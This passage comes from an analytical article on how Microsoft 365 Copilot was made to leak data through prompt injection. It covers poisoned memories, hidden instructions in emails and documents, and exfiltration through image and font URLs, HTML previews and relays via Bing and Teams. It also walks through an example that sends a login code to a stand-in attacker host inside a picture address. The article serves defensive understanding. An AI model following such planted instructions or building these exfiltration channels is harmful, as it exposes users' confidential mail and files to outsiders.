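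The CoSnitch flaws were in the consumer product, as Notebookcheck also notes, so they are not evidence that the same link or web page would have worked against Microsoft 365 Copilot. Varonis presents CoSnitch as a danger to enterprises, and an employee does create such a danger by connecting a work account to a personal assistant.

### Who decides what to remember

In *Unlock the power of personalization*, Microsoft's introduction to the enterprise feature, Bothra (2025) wrote that Copilot saves information only when there is a clear intent to remember it. For example, it would save a user's stated preference for Python in data science, but not a request to write a particular piece of Python code. The model judged whether the intent was clear, and a planted instruction could influence that judgement. Rehberger reported his first memory attacks to Microsoft in the same month the introduction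 was published.

Companies have already found a simpler way to supply the intent, using links that open the user's assistant with a prompt already filled in. Over 60 days, researchers at Microsoft (2026) found 50 different prompts of this kind in links that people had received by email. The prompts came from 31 companies, including one that sold security products. The links were behind buttons labelled "Summarize with AI", and the prompts asked for a summary but also told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source.

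These were advertisers, and Microsoft counted their attempts rather than the memories they planted. The method is still relevant to data theft. As with Reprompt, the prompt in the link looks like the user's own message, and here it contains an explicit request to remember something. A check that compares the memory with the user's apparent intent would therefore find a match.

Rehberger accepts saving a memory automatically when the user's original message clearly asks for it. Otherwise, he thinks the assistant should probably suggest the memory and let the user decide. Microsoft's current help page describes a similar arrangement, in which Copilot saves immediately when the user tells it to remember something but asks first when something merely seems important.

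The case for asking users to confirm is stronger with memories than with most tool calls. People who see too many requests start approving them without reading, but memories should need fewer requests. Marta might need Copilot to search her mail twenty times a day, while she probably wants it to learn something new about her only now and then. A bad memory can also do more harm than a bad search, because it can affect every later answer instead of just one.

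How Copilot asks the user for confirmation matters more than whether it asks. If it asks in the chat, planted text can change the question, as it did in the biography attack and in SafeBreach's forged consent. A question can also mislead by omission. "Shall I remember that you like codes shown in a preview?" would have described Rehberger's planted memory fairly, except that it doesn't mention the server.

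A dialog outside the chat, like Cowork's for outgoing email, could instead show the exact text of the memory and the document that was open when the model proposed it. Marta would then see that her supposed preference contained a stranger's web address and came from an Einstein biography, which would give her good reason to refuse. The dialog would protect her less well against the advertisers, because a request to treat a company as a trusted source looks harmless even in full.

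Even a genuine confirmation dialog helps only if the attack has to trigger it. Cisco demonstrated this with Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for programmers. The agent offered to install the software packages a project needed, and the user approved this routine step. The installation then ran hidden code that overwrote the agent's memory files. A confirmation dialog attached to a memory tool would not have appeared, because the code changed the files directly.

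In its June account, Microsoft proposes two principles for future work: a memory should carry clear information about where it came from, and deterministic systems, not instructions to the model, should control access to memory. A record of origin would be useful even after a successful attack. If Marta's employer discovered that the biography was poisoned, it could delete every memory Copilot had saved in a conversation containing it. Without that record, someone would have to read through each user's list and guess which memories to delete.

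Users have one other control, the custom instructions they type into Copilot's settings. Copilot at Work's *Making Copilot Memory work for you* tested a custom instruction that contradicted a saved memory about the meaning of "football", and Copilot consistently followed the custom instruction. A custom instruction might also override a planted memory that it directly contradicts, but users wouldn't know to write one in advance against a preference they have never heard of.

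### When documents do the remembering

Even if an organisation turns memory off, instructions can persist in its files. Måløy hid instructions in a document that a user then gave to Copilot in Word as source material for a financial report. Copilot halved figures in the report and copied the hidden instructions into it. When a colleague used that report as a source for another, Copilot did the same again without needing the original document. iTnews reported that Copilot could also find a file with hidden instructions by itself while searching the user's OneDrive.

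This attack falsifies information rather than sending it out, but Microsoft's attempts to fix it show that a guardrail may do little against a reworded instruction. On 3 April 2026, Microsoft released a new editing feature in Word. Six days later, Måløy confirmed that his original wording no longer worked, but he succeeded with a different one the same day. Microsoft upgraded the underlying model to GPT-5.5 on 14 July, and the next day Måløy reproduced the attack on the even newer GPT-5.6. When En Klype Salt published the findings on 28 July, the attack still worked and Microsoft had no robust fix for flaws of this kind.

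Saved memories are easier to find and delete than poisoned reports, because they are all in one place where a user or an administrator can read them. Poisoned reports are scattered among an organisation's ordinary files, and their instructions are written in white text on a white background.

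## Rendered replies that make the user's browser send data out

An attacker who plants instructions in a memory or a report still needs a way to get data out. In Rehberger's biography attack, the user's browser sent the password out in a request for a font. This works because browsers request files such as fonts when they load a page.

A page's pictures and fonts are usually separate files, as are many of the stylesheets that set its colours and layout. The page contains only the addresses of these files, and the browser automatically requests each one from the server at its address, because users don't want to approve every file.

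Suppose an ordering site emails Marta a six-digit login code, 482913. Another email contains hidden text that makes Copilot find the code and put it in the address of a picture. Four things then happen:

1. The model writes a reply that includes the address `https://pictures.example/482913.png`.
2. The chat pane converts the reply into HTML, the language of web pages, with a picture at that address.
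3. Marta's browser asks the server at pictures.example for a file called 482913.png.
4. The server records the request in its log, where the attacker reads the code.

The server doesn't need to have such a picture, because it receives the code with the request. Marta may see a broken-picture icon, or nothing if the attacker sends back a transparent pixel. Encryption protects the request from eavesdroppers, but not from the attacker's server, which is the intended recipient. Login codes usually expire within minutes, but the request takes less than a second.

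A font or background image referenced in a stylesheet would send the code out just as well. A link would too, but only after Marta clicked it.

### How the browser decides what to load

The browser can refuse to make the request if the page has a Content Security Policy. W3C, the web's main standards body, sets out the procedure in its working draft *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026). Several of a policy's directives each list the permitted addresses for one type of resource: `img-src` for pictures, `font-src` for fonts, and `connect-src` for connections that the page's scripts open. `default-src` covers any type for which the policy sets no directive.

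Before each request, the browser finds the directive for that type of resource and compares the address with the list. If the address isn't listed, the browser doesn't send the request. If a permitted server redirects the browser to another address, the browser checks that one too.

Suppose the page around Marta's chat pane has this policy, in which the asterisk permits any server:

`default-src 'none'; img-src https://bikes.example; connect-src https://bikes.example; font-src *`

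| Request to pictures.example | Directive that applies | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Picture in the reply | `img-src` | Blocked |
| Background picture named in a stylesheet | `img-src` | Blocked |
| Connection opened by a script | `connect-src` | Blocked |
| Video | `default-src` | Blocked |
| Font | `font-src` | Sent, with the code in the address |

The attacker needs only one of these requests to succeed. If A_k is the set of addresses that the policy permits for resource type k, stolen data can go to any address in the union of those sets:

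`A_img ∪ A_font ∪ A_connect ∪ ...`

This policy lets fonts load from any address, so the browser could still send the code out in a font request even if the company blocked all images. The W3C warns that a policy protects against exfiltration only as well as its least restrictive directive.

The strict default has no effect on fonts because, as MDN's reference page *Content-Security-Policy* explains, the default doesn't apply to a type that has its own directive. A page that forbids pictures, scripts and fonts but has no default can still leak data through unlisted types, such as prefetching, in which the browser loads something before the user needs it.

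W3C recommends CSP as an extra layer of defence against injected content, not the first one. The policy above controls only what the page loads, so it would not stop Marta from clicking a link to pictures.example.

### From pictures to links

Researchers were using images to get data out of chatbots by early 2023. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) described an attack by Roman Samoilenko in which a website added instructions to any text a visitor copied. If the visitor pasted that text into ChatGPT, the reply could contain a one-pixel image with chat data in its URL. OpenAI started to mitigate this in December 2023.

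Rehberger reported a similar flaw in Microsoft's Bing Chat, a forerunner of Copilot, on 8 April 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the chatbot could read the web page the user had open, so a comment or advertisement on that page could hijack it without the victim pasting anything. In the demonstration, the planted text made Bing Chat wait two turns and then display a picture whose address contained a 200-character summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from the page.

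Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June 2023 that it had fixed the flaw. Bing Chat now had a CSP that allowed images from only four Bing addresses, which appears to have been at least part of the fix.

With the picture route closed, Rehberger used links in the Microsoft 365 Copilot attack of February 2024. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes the full attack chain. The hidden instructions could arrive in an email or a shared document, and Copilot searched for other messages without asking the user. The link in its reply carried the results in invisible Unicode characters that correspond to ordinary letters and digits. If Marta's login code, 482913, had been in such a link, she would have seen only a normal address, and clicking it would have sent the code. Rehberger demonstrated this with sales figures and login codes for Slack, a workplace chat service.

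Rehberger first reported the invisible characters by themselves on 17 January 2024. Microsoft closed that report a day later as low severity. Microsoft opened a case only after he submitted the whole chain on 10 February, though he had already pointed out that the characters would matter more as part of an attack.

He recommended that Copilot stop searching automatically, stop displaying the hidden characters and, ideally, stop displaying links. By 2 July his demonstration no longer worked, and Copilot appeared to have stopped displaying links. Microsoft did not answer his request for details of the fix.

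Another clickable route emerged in 2025. Copilot could draw diagrams from a text notation called Mermaid, and a diagram could contain a link. Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* reports that the researcher Adam Logue hid instructions in white text across several sheets of an Excel file. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot followed the hidden instructions instead, and clicking the resulting diagram sent out recent emails. By 26 September 2025, Microsoft had fixed this by removing interactive links from the diagrams.

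### The HTML preview

At about the same time, Rehberger noticed that Microsoft 365 Copilot could display a small web page in a panel inside the chat. The panel's Code view showed the HTML, and its Preview view showed the finished page.

Such a preview is an exfiltration channel if it can load files from any server. Embrace The Red describes two obstacles that at first seemed to prevent this. Copilot removed HTML image tags, so when Rehberger asked for a page with a heading and a picture from his server, only the heading appeared. The panel also opened in Code view, so no request would go out unless the user switched to Preview.

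Rehberger then had Copilot write a page with as many ways of loading an outside file as it could generate. One that worked was a stylesheet that specified a background image. The filter removed image tags, but a stylesheet can load an image without one. The browser still applied the CSP's image directive, which blocked requests to unlisted servers. However, the list of permitted addresses was long and differed between host applications.

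Again with Copilot's help, he found that a stylesheet could also request a font. The CSP's font directive was looser than its image directive and let the browser contact his server. Microsoft had restricted images in both the filter and the CSP, but neither restriction applied to fonts.

The second obstacle was easier to overcome. Rehberger changed the planted text to also ask for the preview, and Copilot reliably opened it. Microsoft had let the model switch to Preview, so the default view no longer protected users once an attacker had hijacked the model.

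In the Word demonstration, hidden instructions in the shared document made Copilot respond to a greeting by searching the victim's mail for a message with the subject "The Code". Copilot then wrote a web page, put the message's contents into a font's URL and opened the preview. The browser requested the font from Rehberger's server, and he read the message in the request.

The same route worked in desktop Word, Word Online and Excel Online. It could have carried Teams messages or anything else Copilot could read.

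| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 16 October 2025 | Rehberger reports the background-picture and font requests to Microsoft |
| 18 October 2025 | Microsoft opens an internal case |
| 20 October 2025 | Rehberger realises that the CSP depends on the host application |
| 12 November 2025 | Microsoft confirms that it can reproduce the flaw |
| 19 November 2025 | Rehberger sends the version that persists through a saved memory |
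| 17 December 2025 | Microsoft awards a bounty |
| 25 February 2026 | Microsoft is rolling out a fix |
| 5 March 2026 | Microsoft marks the case as fixed |

The fix took 140 days, about twice as long as the one for Bing Chat. Rehberger doesn't explain what Microsoft changed, and there is no explanation in the public record. Microsoft may have removed more elements from the preview, tightened the font directive or stopped the preview from loading any outside files. These changes would differ considerably in how well they protect against the next variation of the attack.

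MITRE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the public record for CVE-2026-24299, appeared on 19 March 2026. Microsoft rated the flaw 5.3 out of 10 (medium severity), despite a high impact on confidentiality. CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, recorded no known exploitation.

Microsoft rated the attack as requiring user interaction, while Rehberger calls it zero-click. Both descriptions fit, since the victim still had to use Copilot. The score would rise only to 5.9 if the attack were rated as requiring no interaction. Microsoft also rated the attack as highly complex, which lowered the score more, by about 1.2 points. That rating is questionable, since the attacker only had to share a document and the demonstrations worked in three applications.

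### Removing what is dangerous or permitting what is safe

Copilot's preview removed an element that Microsoft knew to be dangerous but displayed much of the rest. Microsoft's 2025 account of its defences includes "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods", but such blocking doesn't stop methods that Microsoft hasn't identified.

The alternative is to permit a short list of elements known to be safe, such as headings, paragraphs, tables and bold type, and to drop everything else or show it as plain text. Data can then leak only if one of the permitted elements can send it out, so the developer needs to examine only those few. A developer who instead removes dangerous features has to find every feature that can send data out, including any that nobody has discovered yet, because data can leak through any that are missed.

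If a browser gains a new way to load files, a removal filter lets it through until someone updates the filter, while a permission filter blocks it until someone approves it.

The same mistake can occur when a single feature can be written in more than one way. *EchoLeak* documents an attack in which Copilot's filter removed external links and images written in the usual notation but missed those written in a less common one.

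Removal keeps more of what users want. Someone who asks Copilot to design a web page expects to see its colours and layout, which an allowlist of headings and tables would discard. Removal is also quick to deploy after a report. But attackers can easily search for omissions, as Rehberger did by asking Copilot for a list. Microsoft could have run the same test before releasing the preview.

A permission list has to be detailed to be useful. If the developer permits stylesheets as a single feature, the list also allows fonts and background pictures, and Rehberger's attack still works. A safe list permits colours and spacing but no outside addresses.

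CSP can add a second check of this kind. A browser enforces every policy that applies to a page, so a preview in its own frame can have a stricter policy than the page around it:

`default-src 'none'; style-src 'unsafe-inline'`

The second directive lets the preview use styles written into the page. Everything else falls back to the default, which allows no addresses, so the browser would block the background picture and the font. The user would see the layout with standard fonts and a gap where an outside picture belonged. That seems a small loss for a preview, and the user could still open the finished page elsewhere.

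Google went further with Generative AI Studio, a tool for developers on its cloud platform. After Rehberger showed that pictures could leak the chat history there, Google apparently stopped displaying links as well as pictures. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* calls this probably the best possible fix for security. The same change would inconvenience users of an office assistant more. Marta uses links in Copilot's answers to open and check the contract, so her employer would probably prefer to keep links to its own files and drop the others.

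A permitted domain can become unsafe if its registration expires. Willison's *41 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce. Salesforce's CSP allowed images only from listed domains, but one of those domains had expired. Researchers registered it and received customer data through an image. By 26 September 2025, Salesforce had corrected the list and added a check on the addresses its agent could put in a reply.

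An attacker may not need to own a permitted address. SearchLeak, a one-click attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, combined a timing flaw in how HTML was displayed with a permitted Bing service that forwarded requests, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool*. Microsoft patched it in June 2026, three months after fixing the preview.

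## Trusted services that pass the data on

SearchLeak could send data through Bing because a CSP applies only to requests the browser makes. The browser checks the address of each request against the policy, but the server that receives the request may then contact other servers, and the policy does not cover those requests.

Take Marta's login code again, 482913, and a page that permits pictures only from bikes.example. Suppose the bicycle maker runs an image-resizing service on that domain. A browser gives the service the address of any picture on the web, and the service fetches the picture and returns a smaller copy. An attacker can use it as a relay:

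1. Hidden text makes Copilot add a picture to its reply. The picture's address points to the resizing service and names `pictures.example/482913.png` as the picture to resize.
2. Marta's browser compares the address with the policy, finds bikes.example and sends the request.
3. The resizing service requests the named picture from pictures.example.
4. The attacker's server records the code in its log.

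The browser never contacted pictures.example, so it had nothing to block. A redirect to pictures.example would have failed, because the browser checks redirects too.

This is server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes someone else's server send a request the attacker chooses. Attackers have long used it to reach systems behind a company's firewall, but here they use it to send data out.

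Let A be the set of all addresses the policy lets the browser contact, and let F(a) be the addresses that the server at a will fetch on request. Stolen data can then reach any address in:

`A ∪ F(a₁) ∪ F(a₂) ∪ ...`

If even one permitted server fetches any address it receives, this set covers the whole public web, however short the rest of the list is. The browser cannot work out F, so the people who write the policy have to know what every service on every permitted domain does, including services that other teams run.

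A relay also hides the destination from the victim's employer. When the relay belongs to Microsoft, the employer's firewall handles only an encrypted request to a Microsoft domain. The request to the attacker's server starts in Microsoft's data centre and never crosses the employer's network.

### EchoLeak and the Teams relay

In January 2025, Aim Labs, Aim Security's research department, found a relay of this kind among Microsoft's services. Its attack, EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), began with an email that anyone outside the organisation could send.

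The email first had to get into Copilot's context window, and Copilot reads only the messages it retrieves for each request. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, assumes for simplicity that the retrieval software represents each passage as a point in a mathematical space, with passages of similar meaning close together, and picks those nearest the question. A short email occupies one point, so the software will retrieve it for few questions. Aim Labs therefore wrote a long email in sections, each presented as a guide to a different office subject, such as onboarding or leave, and repeated the same instructions in every section. Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

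Ravia gives no figure for how often this worked, but most office workers with Copilot would probably soon ask a question that matched one of the sections.

Microsoft's injection classifier did not stop the email, because the email's instructions read like a request to the human recipient. The link filter missed the less common link notation. Copilot normally shows which messages an answer draws on, but the email also contained an instruction never to refer to it, which Copilot followed. The victim would have seen at most a broken image, with nothing to connect it to the email.

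The remaining obstacle was the CSP. The list of permitted image addresses that Ravia published has 29 different entries, 11 of which cover every subdomain of a domain. Aim Labs searched the list for a server that would fetch an outside address. A SharePoint function would, but only if the victim was signed in to SharePoint and had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service for previewing web content would do so without those conditions. Through it, the attack could send out anything in Copilot's context window, including the chat history and any files Copilot had fetched.

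Microsoft finished fixing the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and Aim Labs published the attack on 11 June. According to *EchoLeak*, Microsoft began removing links and images in the less common notation from outside content, and reportedly gave organisations an option to keep external messages out of some of Copilot's work. Before that, as far as Aim Labs knew, administrators had no setting that could have prevented the attack. Both changes restrict what goes into Copilot but don't shorten the list of servers that the browser may contact afterward.

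Ravia locates the main problem earlier in the chain, in what he calls an "LLM scope violation", where text from an untrusted source makes the model use trusted data that the source has no right to, without the user's consent. The planted email asked for the most sensitive item in the rest of Copilot's context, which an ordinary supplier has little reason to do. A filter could look for outside text that refers to data beyond itself, which is a more specific test than suspicious wording. But it could also flag an honest supplier who writes "please check this against our contract". Aim Security developed a guardrail on this principle, so it had a commercial interest in the diagnosis.

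### SearchLeak and why it needed three flaws

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), published on 15 June, describes an attack (CVE-2026-42824) that began with a link and targeted the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot, which finds emails, meetings and files across an organisation.

A link to this page can contain a search query. Copilot treated the query as instructions and carried them out as soon as the page opened, without the victim typing anything. Varonis had used the same kind of entry point for Reprompt, its attack on the consumer version, and was surprised that it also worked against the enterprise version. The link led to a genuine Microsoft domain, which gave no grounds for a domain reputation filter to block it.

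The instructions told Copilot to find an email and put its subject line into the address of a picture. Microsoft's existing safeguard against dangerous HTML marked the reply as code, which makes a browser display an image tag as text instead of loading the picture.

However, Copilot's replies appear on screen while the model is still writing them, and the safeguard ran only once the reply was complete. By the time it converted the image tag to text, the browser had already requested the picture. This is called a race condition, because the result depends on which of two operations happens first. Anyone who tested the safeguard by looking at finished replies would have concluded that it worked.

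The browser still would not load pictures from the attacker's server, but it would load them from Bing, whose search-by-image feature fetches and analyses the picture at a given address. Copilot's reply included the subject line in an address on the attacker's server and passed that address to Bing, which fetched it.

Varonis considers all three flaws necessary, and for this attack they were. If Copilot had treated the query only as a search, the attacker could not have put a picture in the reply. If the safeguard had run before the browser displayed anything, the picture would have stayed text. Without the relay, the CSP would have blocked the request. However, an attacker could replace the first flaw with any other way of giving Copilot instructions, such as an email.

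In the demonstration, the stolen subject line contained a security code. Varonis infers that an attacker could also have taken meeting notes, salary files or anything else the victim could open. This inference is reasonable because Copilot searches with the victim's permissions, but the published example shows the theft of only one subject line.

### One click, one point

Published ratings of SearchLeak range from medium to critical, partly because Microsoft rates it on two scales. Microsoft labels the flaw "Critical" on its own scale but scores it 6.5 out of 10, or medium, on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) attributes the "critical" rating to Varonis, but Varonis was repeating Microsoft's label.

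Other databases show 7.5. The whole difference comes from whether the attack needs the victim to do something. With SearchLeak's other ratings held fixed, the CVSS formula reduces to:

`score = 3.595 + 4.573 × u, rounded up to one decimal place`

The entry *CVE-2026-42824* in one vulnerability database lists user interaction as required, while STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) lists it as "None". The value of u is 0.62 if the victim has to act, which gives a score of 6.5, and 0.85 if not, which gives 7.5.

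The lower score, 6.5, fits the published attack because the victim has to click the link. The higher score, 7.5, appears to have come later or from elsewhere, because the temporal score published with it doesn't match. A CVSS temporal score is the base score reduced to reflect the state of exploit code and fixes. For SearchLeak, the base score is multiplied by 0.91 × 0.95 and rounded up, so 6.5 becomes 5.7 and 7.5 becomes 6.5. STAR Labs lists 7.5 with a temporal score of 5.7, which must have been calculated from 6.5.

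vuln.today's *Microsoft 365 Copilot CVE-2026-42824* (2026) shows the same mismatched pair and attributes the 7.5 to the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD). The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* reports that the NVD entry gave 6.5, the same as Microsoft's. The NVD may have changed its entry in between.

NVD did change the score for EchoLeak. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives it 9.3, while Aqua Security's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), last modified in February 2026, shows an NVD score of 7.5. A flaw that only discloses information cannot score above 8.6 on this scale, so the 9.3 must also include some other harm, such as altered data. The 7.5 covers disclosure alone, and on that basis EchoLeak scores only one point more than SearchLeak (6.5), because SearchLeak requires a click. The gap between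 9.3 and 6.5 overstates the difference between the two flaws.

CISA also treated EchoLeak as more serious than SearchLeak. In an assessment reproduced by GCVE (2025), a public vulnerability database, CISA judged that attackers could automate EchoLeak and that its technical impact was total. It judged that attackers could not automate SearchLeak and that its technical impact was partial.

### ReLeak returns to email

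Aim Security became part of Cato Networks in September 2025, and its researchers now work as Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026 they published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which describes three zero-click attack chains found one year after EchoLeak. All three started with an email. One ran code that contacted an outside server directly, and the other two used Microsoft's services as relays.

The image chain (CVE-2026-124115) put confidential data into the URL of an image in Copilot's reply. The browser loaded the image automatically, and Bing passed the data to the attacker's server. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a Russian report on the research, notes that SearchLeak used a similar channel but needed at least one click. The new chain combined EchoLeak's entry method with SearchLeak's method of sending data out.

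The generated-file chain (CVE-2026-124132) did not need the browser. Planted instructions made Copilot create a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with confidential data in it. Microsoft's servers process files in OneDrive and SharePoint in the background, and processing this file sent the data to the attacker. In the tests Antipov describes, this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the file.

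Neither Antipov nor Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, identifies the background process. Storage services commonly open new files to make thumbnails, index the text or scan for malware, and any of these could involve loading external content.

A CSP could not have stopped the request, whatever process made it, because it did not come from a web page. Sanitising Copilot's replies would not help either if the dangerous address is in a file, and even an alert user could not have stopped the theft by closing the chat. Microsoft could prevent such a leak by checking files before Copilot saves them or by blocking the background process from contacting outside addresses. The second measure seems more dependable because it doesn't require a filter to recognise every kind of link in four file formats.

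Cato reported its findings between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed the file chain on 11 November and the image chain on 15 November. It made both fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install.

| Chain | Entry point | Relay | User action | Severity | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Email | Teams preview service | Asks Copilot a question | 9.3; later 7.5 from NVD | May 2025 |
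| SearchLeak | Prompt in a link | Bing image search | Clicks the link | 6.5; "Critical" on Microsoft's own scale | June 2026 |
| ReLeak, images | Email | Bing | Asks Copilot a question | No confirmed public score at disclosure | 15 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, files | Email | Background processing in OneDrive and SharePoint | Asks Copilot a question | No confirmed public score at disclosure | 11 November 2026 |

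### No known victims

The researchers reported no known exploitation of any of these chains. Aim Labs knew of no affected customers when it published EchoLeak, and Ravia adds that Microsoft had confirmed there were none. Microsoft found no evidence of malicious use of SearchLeak, according to The Next Web. Cato knew of no real attacks or affected customers when it disclosed ReLeak.

This is fairly good evidence against a large campaign. Microsoft fixed each flaw before the details became public, so criminals would have had to find it on their own. Thousands of copies of the same strange email would also probably have attracted attention.

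It is much weaker evidence that nobody ever used one of the flaws against a few chosen targets. Outside researchers cannot search other companies' mailboxes or Microsoft's server records. Victims would have had little to report, since they would have seen a broken picture with EchoLeak and an odd search result with SearchLeak. Microsoft can check more easily because the stolen data passed through its servers. But Bing's image search is designed to fetch pictures from outside addresses, so a theft would look like ordinary use unless someone examined the addresses closely. Ravia does not explain how Microsoft reached its conclusion about EchoLeak.

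### What the patches left in place

The list of permitted addresses that Ravia published in 2025 included Teams, which EchoLeak used, and every subdomain of bing.com. A year later, SearchLeak sent its data through Bing. Microsoft patched SearchLeak in June 2026, and within about ten weeks Cato reported another chain that went through Bing.

Bing could still relay data after the June patch, perhaps because SearchLeak needed all three flaws and Microsoft could stop it by repairing any one of them. Varonis does not say which one Microsoft repaired. If it repaired only the link or the timing of the safeguard, Bing would still have relayed data for anyone who found another way to put a picture in a reply. If it restricted the search-by-image feature, Cato must have found a way around the restriction or another Bing service that fetches outside addresses.

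Bing is hard to drop from the list, presumably because Copilot shows images from Bing's search results. Bing's image search would be of little use if it couldn't fetch images from other sites. Allowing Bing and letting it fetch outside images each make sense to the team responsible, which may be why the combination lasted so long.

The entry point for these attacks also remained open. Faisal reports that Microsoft's protections against injection failed to block any of the three ReLeak chains, which Cato reported more than a year after Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak. The researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made". Cato sells security products for AI, so it benefits from that message, but its own results support the conclusion about the entry point, since Copilot could still take instructions from a stranger's unopened email.

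The Next Web overstated the pattern in June when it described Reprompt, EchoLeak and SearchLeak as three disclosures in six months that each got past the protections from the previous fix. EchoLeak and SearchLeak were a year apart, and Reprompt affected a different product. Microsoft's individual patches may well have held, but it kept adding features that could fetch an address, such as file creation, and each of them gave researchers somewhere new to look.

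Such features are also becoming easier to find. Cato used AI agents to find the ReLeak flaws. Antipov reports that the agents, directed by the researchers, wrote test scenarios, analysed Copilot's refusals and used them to adjust the next attempt.

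## One copilot in many host applications, with different protections

Microsoft protects Copilot differently in different applications, so an attacker's hidden instructions may fail in one and succeed in another. While testing the HTML preview, Johann Rehberger found that SharePoint Online, Excel Online and BizChat, the standalone chat page of Microsoft 365 Copilot, each had a different CSP.

Copilot's tools also differed between hosts. When Rehberger last checked, Copilot in Outlook had no memory tool, so a poisoned email could not have planted a false memory there. Embrace The Red also lists Word Online, desktop Outlook and the Microsoft 365 app among the hosts that behave differently, and reports that Microsoft now has over 80 products called Copilot.

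Microsoft also records some flaws separately for each host application. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21521* (2026) covers a January flaw in Word's Copilot that let an attacker with no account obtain data. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-55145* (2026) covers a July flaw in Outlook's Copilot that an attacker could exploit only if they already had some access. Both entries list an official fix.

### What the lists allowed

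Some of the addresses on the CSP lists were subdomains of azureedge.net, which Microsoft's cloud customers have used to deliver files to browsers. Each customer decides how their subdomain handles requests, and an attacker can be a customer. Microsoft is retiring the service, which should make new subdomains harder to get, but customers still control many existing ones.

Other entries pointed to pre-production sites, including some labelled "dogfood", the industry's term for software that a company tests on its own staff. Developers test unfinished features on such sites, and one that fetches outside addresses could serve as a relay. A few entries contained what looked like employees' user names, and Rehberger suspects that individual employees had added their own domains. If so, it's not obvious who would remove an entry after its owner changed jobs.

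Rehberger didn't show data leaving through any of these addresses. He had thought about mapping each host's list to look for gaps, but the looser rules for fonts gave him a route that worked in many hosts. His account is good evidence that the lists differed and that Microsoft controlled them loosely, but it doesn't establish which host was weakest.

### Which page's policy applies

If a developer builds the chat pane directly into the host's page, the host's policy controls the pictures and fonts in Copilot's replies. The same pane, with the same code, then has strict rules in one host and loose rules in another.

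A developer can instead put the pane in a frame, which is a page displayed inside another page. The inner page normally comes from the widget maker's server with its own policy, and the browser applies that policy to the replies. The host's policy controls only which addresses the frame may load from. A host policy that forbids outside pictures therefore does not block them inside the frame.

Under the W3C's rules, when a page supplies a frame's content directly instead of fetching it from a server, the browser gives the frame a copy of the page's policy. The developer can add restrictions but not remove any. Supplying the content directly is a natural way to build an HTML preview, since the model has just written the HTML and no server has it. It would explain why Copilot's preview had different rules in different hosts, though Microsoft could also have served a different frame to each host.

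Desktop Word isn't a web page, so it has no CSP to pass on. Desktop programs commonly display a chat pane in a built-in browser, which enforces the policy of whatever page it loads. If that page is part of the installed program, no server sends a policy with it, so the developer has to write one into the page. Without one, the pane could load files from anywhere unless the program itself blocks them. The program can also fetch files with its own code, which CSP doesn't cover. Rehberger's font attack worked in desktop Word as well as online, despite any restrictions Microsoft had there.

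### The same email in Outlook and Teams

Hosts can also differ in how readily the assistant follows planted instructions. *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH*, by the security company Permiso, compares three ways to summarise an email with Copilot: the Summarize button in Outlook, the chat pane beside the inbox, and Copilot in Teams.

When the email contained little besides a blatant instruction, Copilot detected it and refused. The researchers then placed the instruction in a longer, more ordinary message. The Summarize button sometimes gave a normal summary and sometimes included traces of the planted text. The chat pane usually ignored the instruction but complied in some email programs. Copilot in Teams was the most likely to add the attacker's text to its summary. This ranking is rough because Permiso gives no success rates.

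In the most serious result, Copilot looked up recent Teams messages and put them into a link beneath a fake security warning. Clicking the link would have sent the messages outside the company.

Permiso also observes that users think of Copilot as one product and tend to use whichever version answers them. If the pane in Outlook refuses to summarise a poisoned email, Marta may ask Copilot in Teams instead. The attacker would not have to do anything to move her from a host that protected her to one that might not.

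Microsoft told Permiso on 11 March 2026 that it had finished fixing the flaw in every affected version. Some of those versions were phone apps. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-26133* (2026) lists separate fixed versions for the Copilot app on Android and on iOS, and for the Edge browser on Android. Appaloosa's *CVE-2026-26133* adds the mobile versions of Excel, OneNote, Outlook, PowerPoint and Teams. Microsoft can change a web page for everyone at once on its own servers, but a phone may stay vulnerable until its owner updates the app.

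A flaw in the host application can also expose data through the assistant. Excel had a cross-site scripting flaw that let a workbook contain code that ran as if it belonged to the program. Microsoft warned, in a notice quoted by Briefly, that an attacker could use the flaw to make Copilot's Agent mode send data out without the user clicking anything. Mishcon de Reya's *Zero‑click excel bug weaponizes Copilot for data disclosure* (2026) dates the patch to 10 March 2026. Training the model to ignore planted instructions would not have fixed the flaw, because it was in Excel.

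### What an attacker gains by choosing the host

Let A(h) be the set of outside addresses that host h permits. An attacker who can use only one host can send data only to the addresses in that host's set. An attacker who can choose the host can use any address in the union:

`A(h₁) ∪ A(h₂) ∪ ... ∪ A(hₙ)`

An attacker can often choose the host application just by choosing the file type, because people usually open workbooks in Excel and documents in Word. SearchLeak instead used a link that opened the Copilot page the attack needed.

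In this example, which uses three invented hosts, the bicycle maker has the same copilot in a mail page, a spreadsheet page and a parts portal. The attacker uses hidden text to instruct the copilot to send Marta's login code to parts.cloud.example. The attacker rents that address from a hosting company that gives every customer a subdomain of cloud.example.

| Invented host | Outside addresses it permits | Request to parts.cloud.example |
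|---|---|---|
| Mail page | photos.example | Blocked |
| Spreadsheet page | photos.example, charts.example | Blocked |
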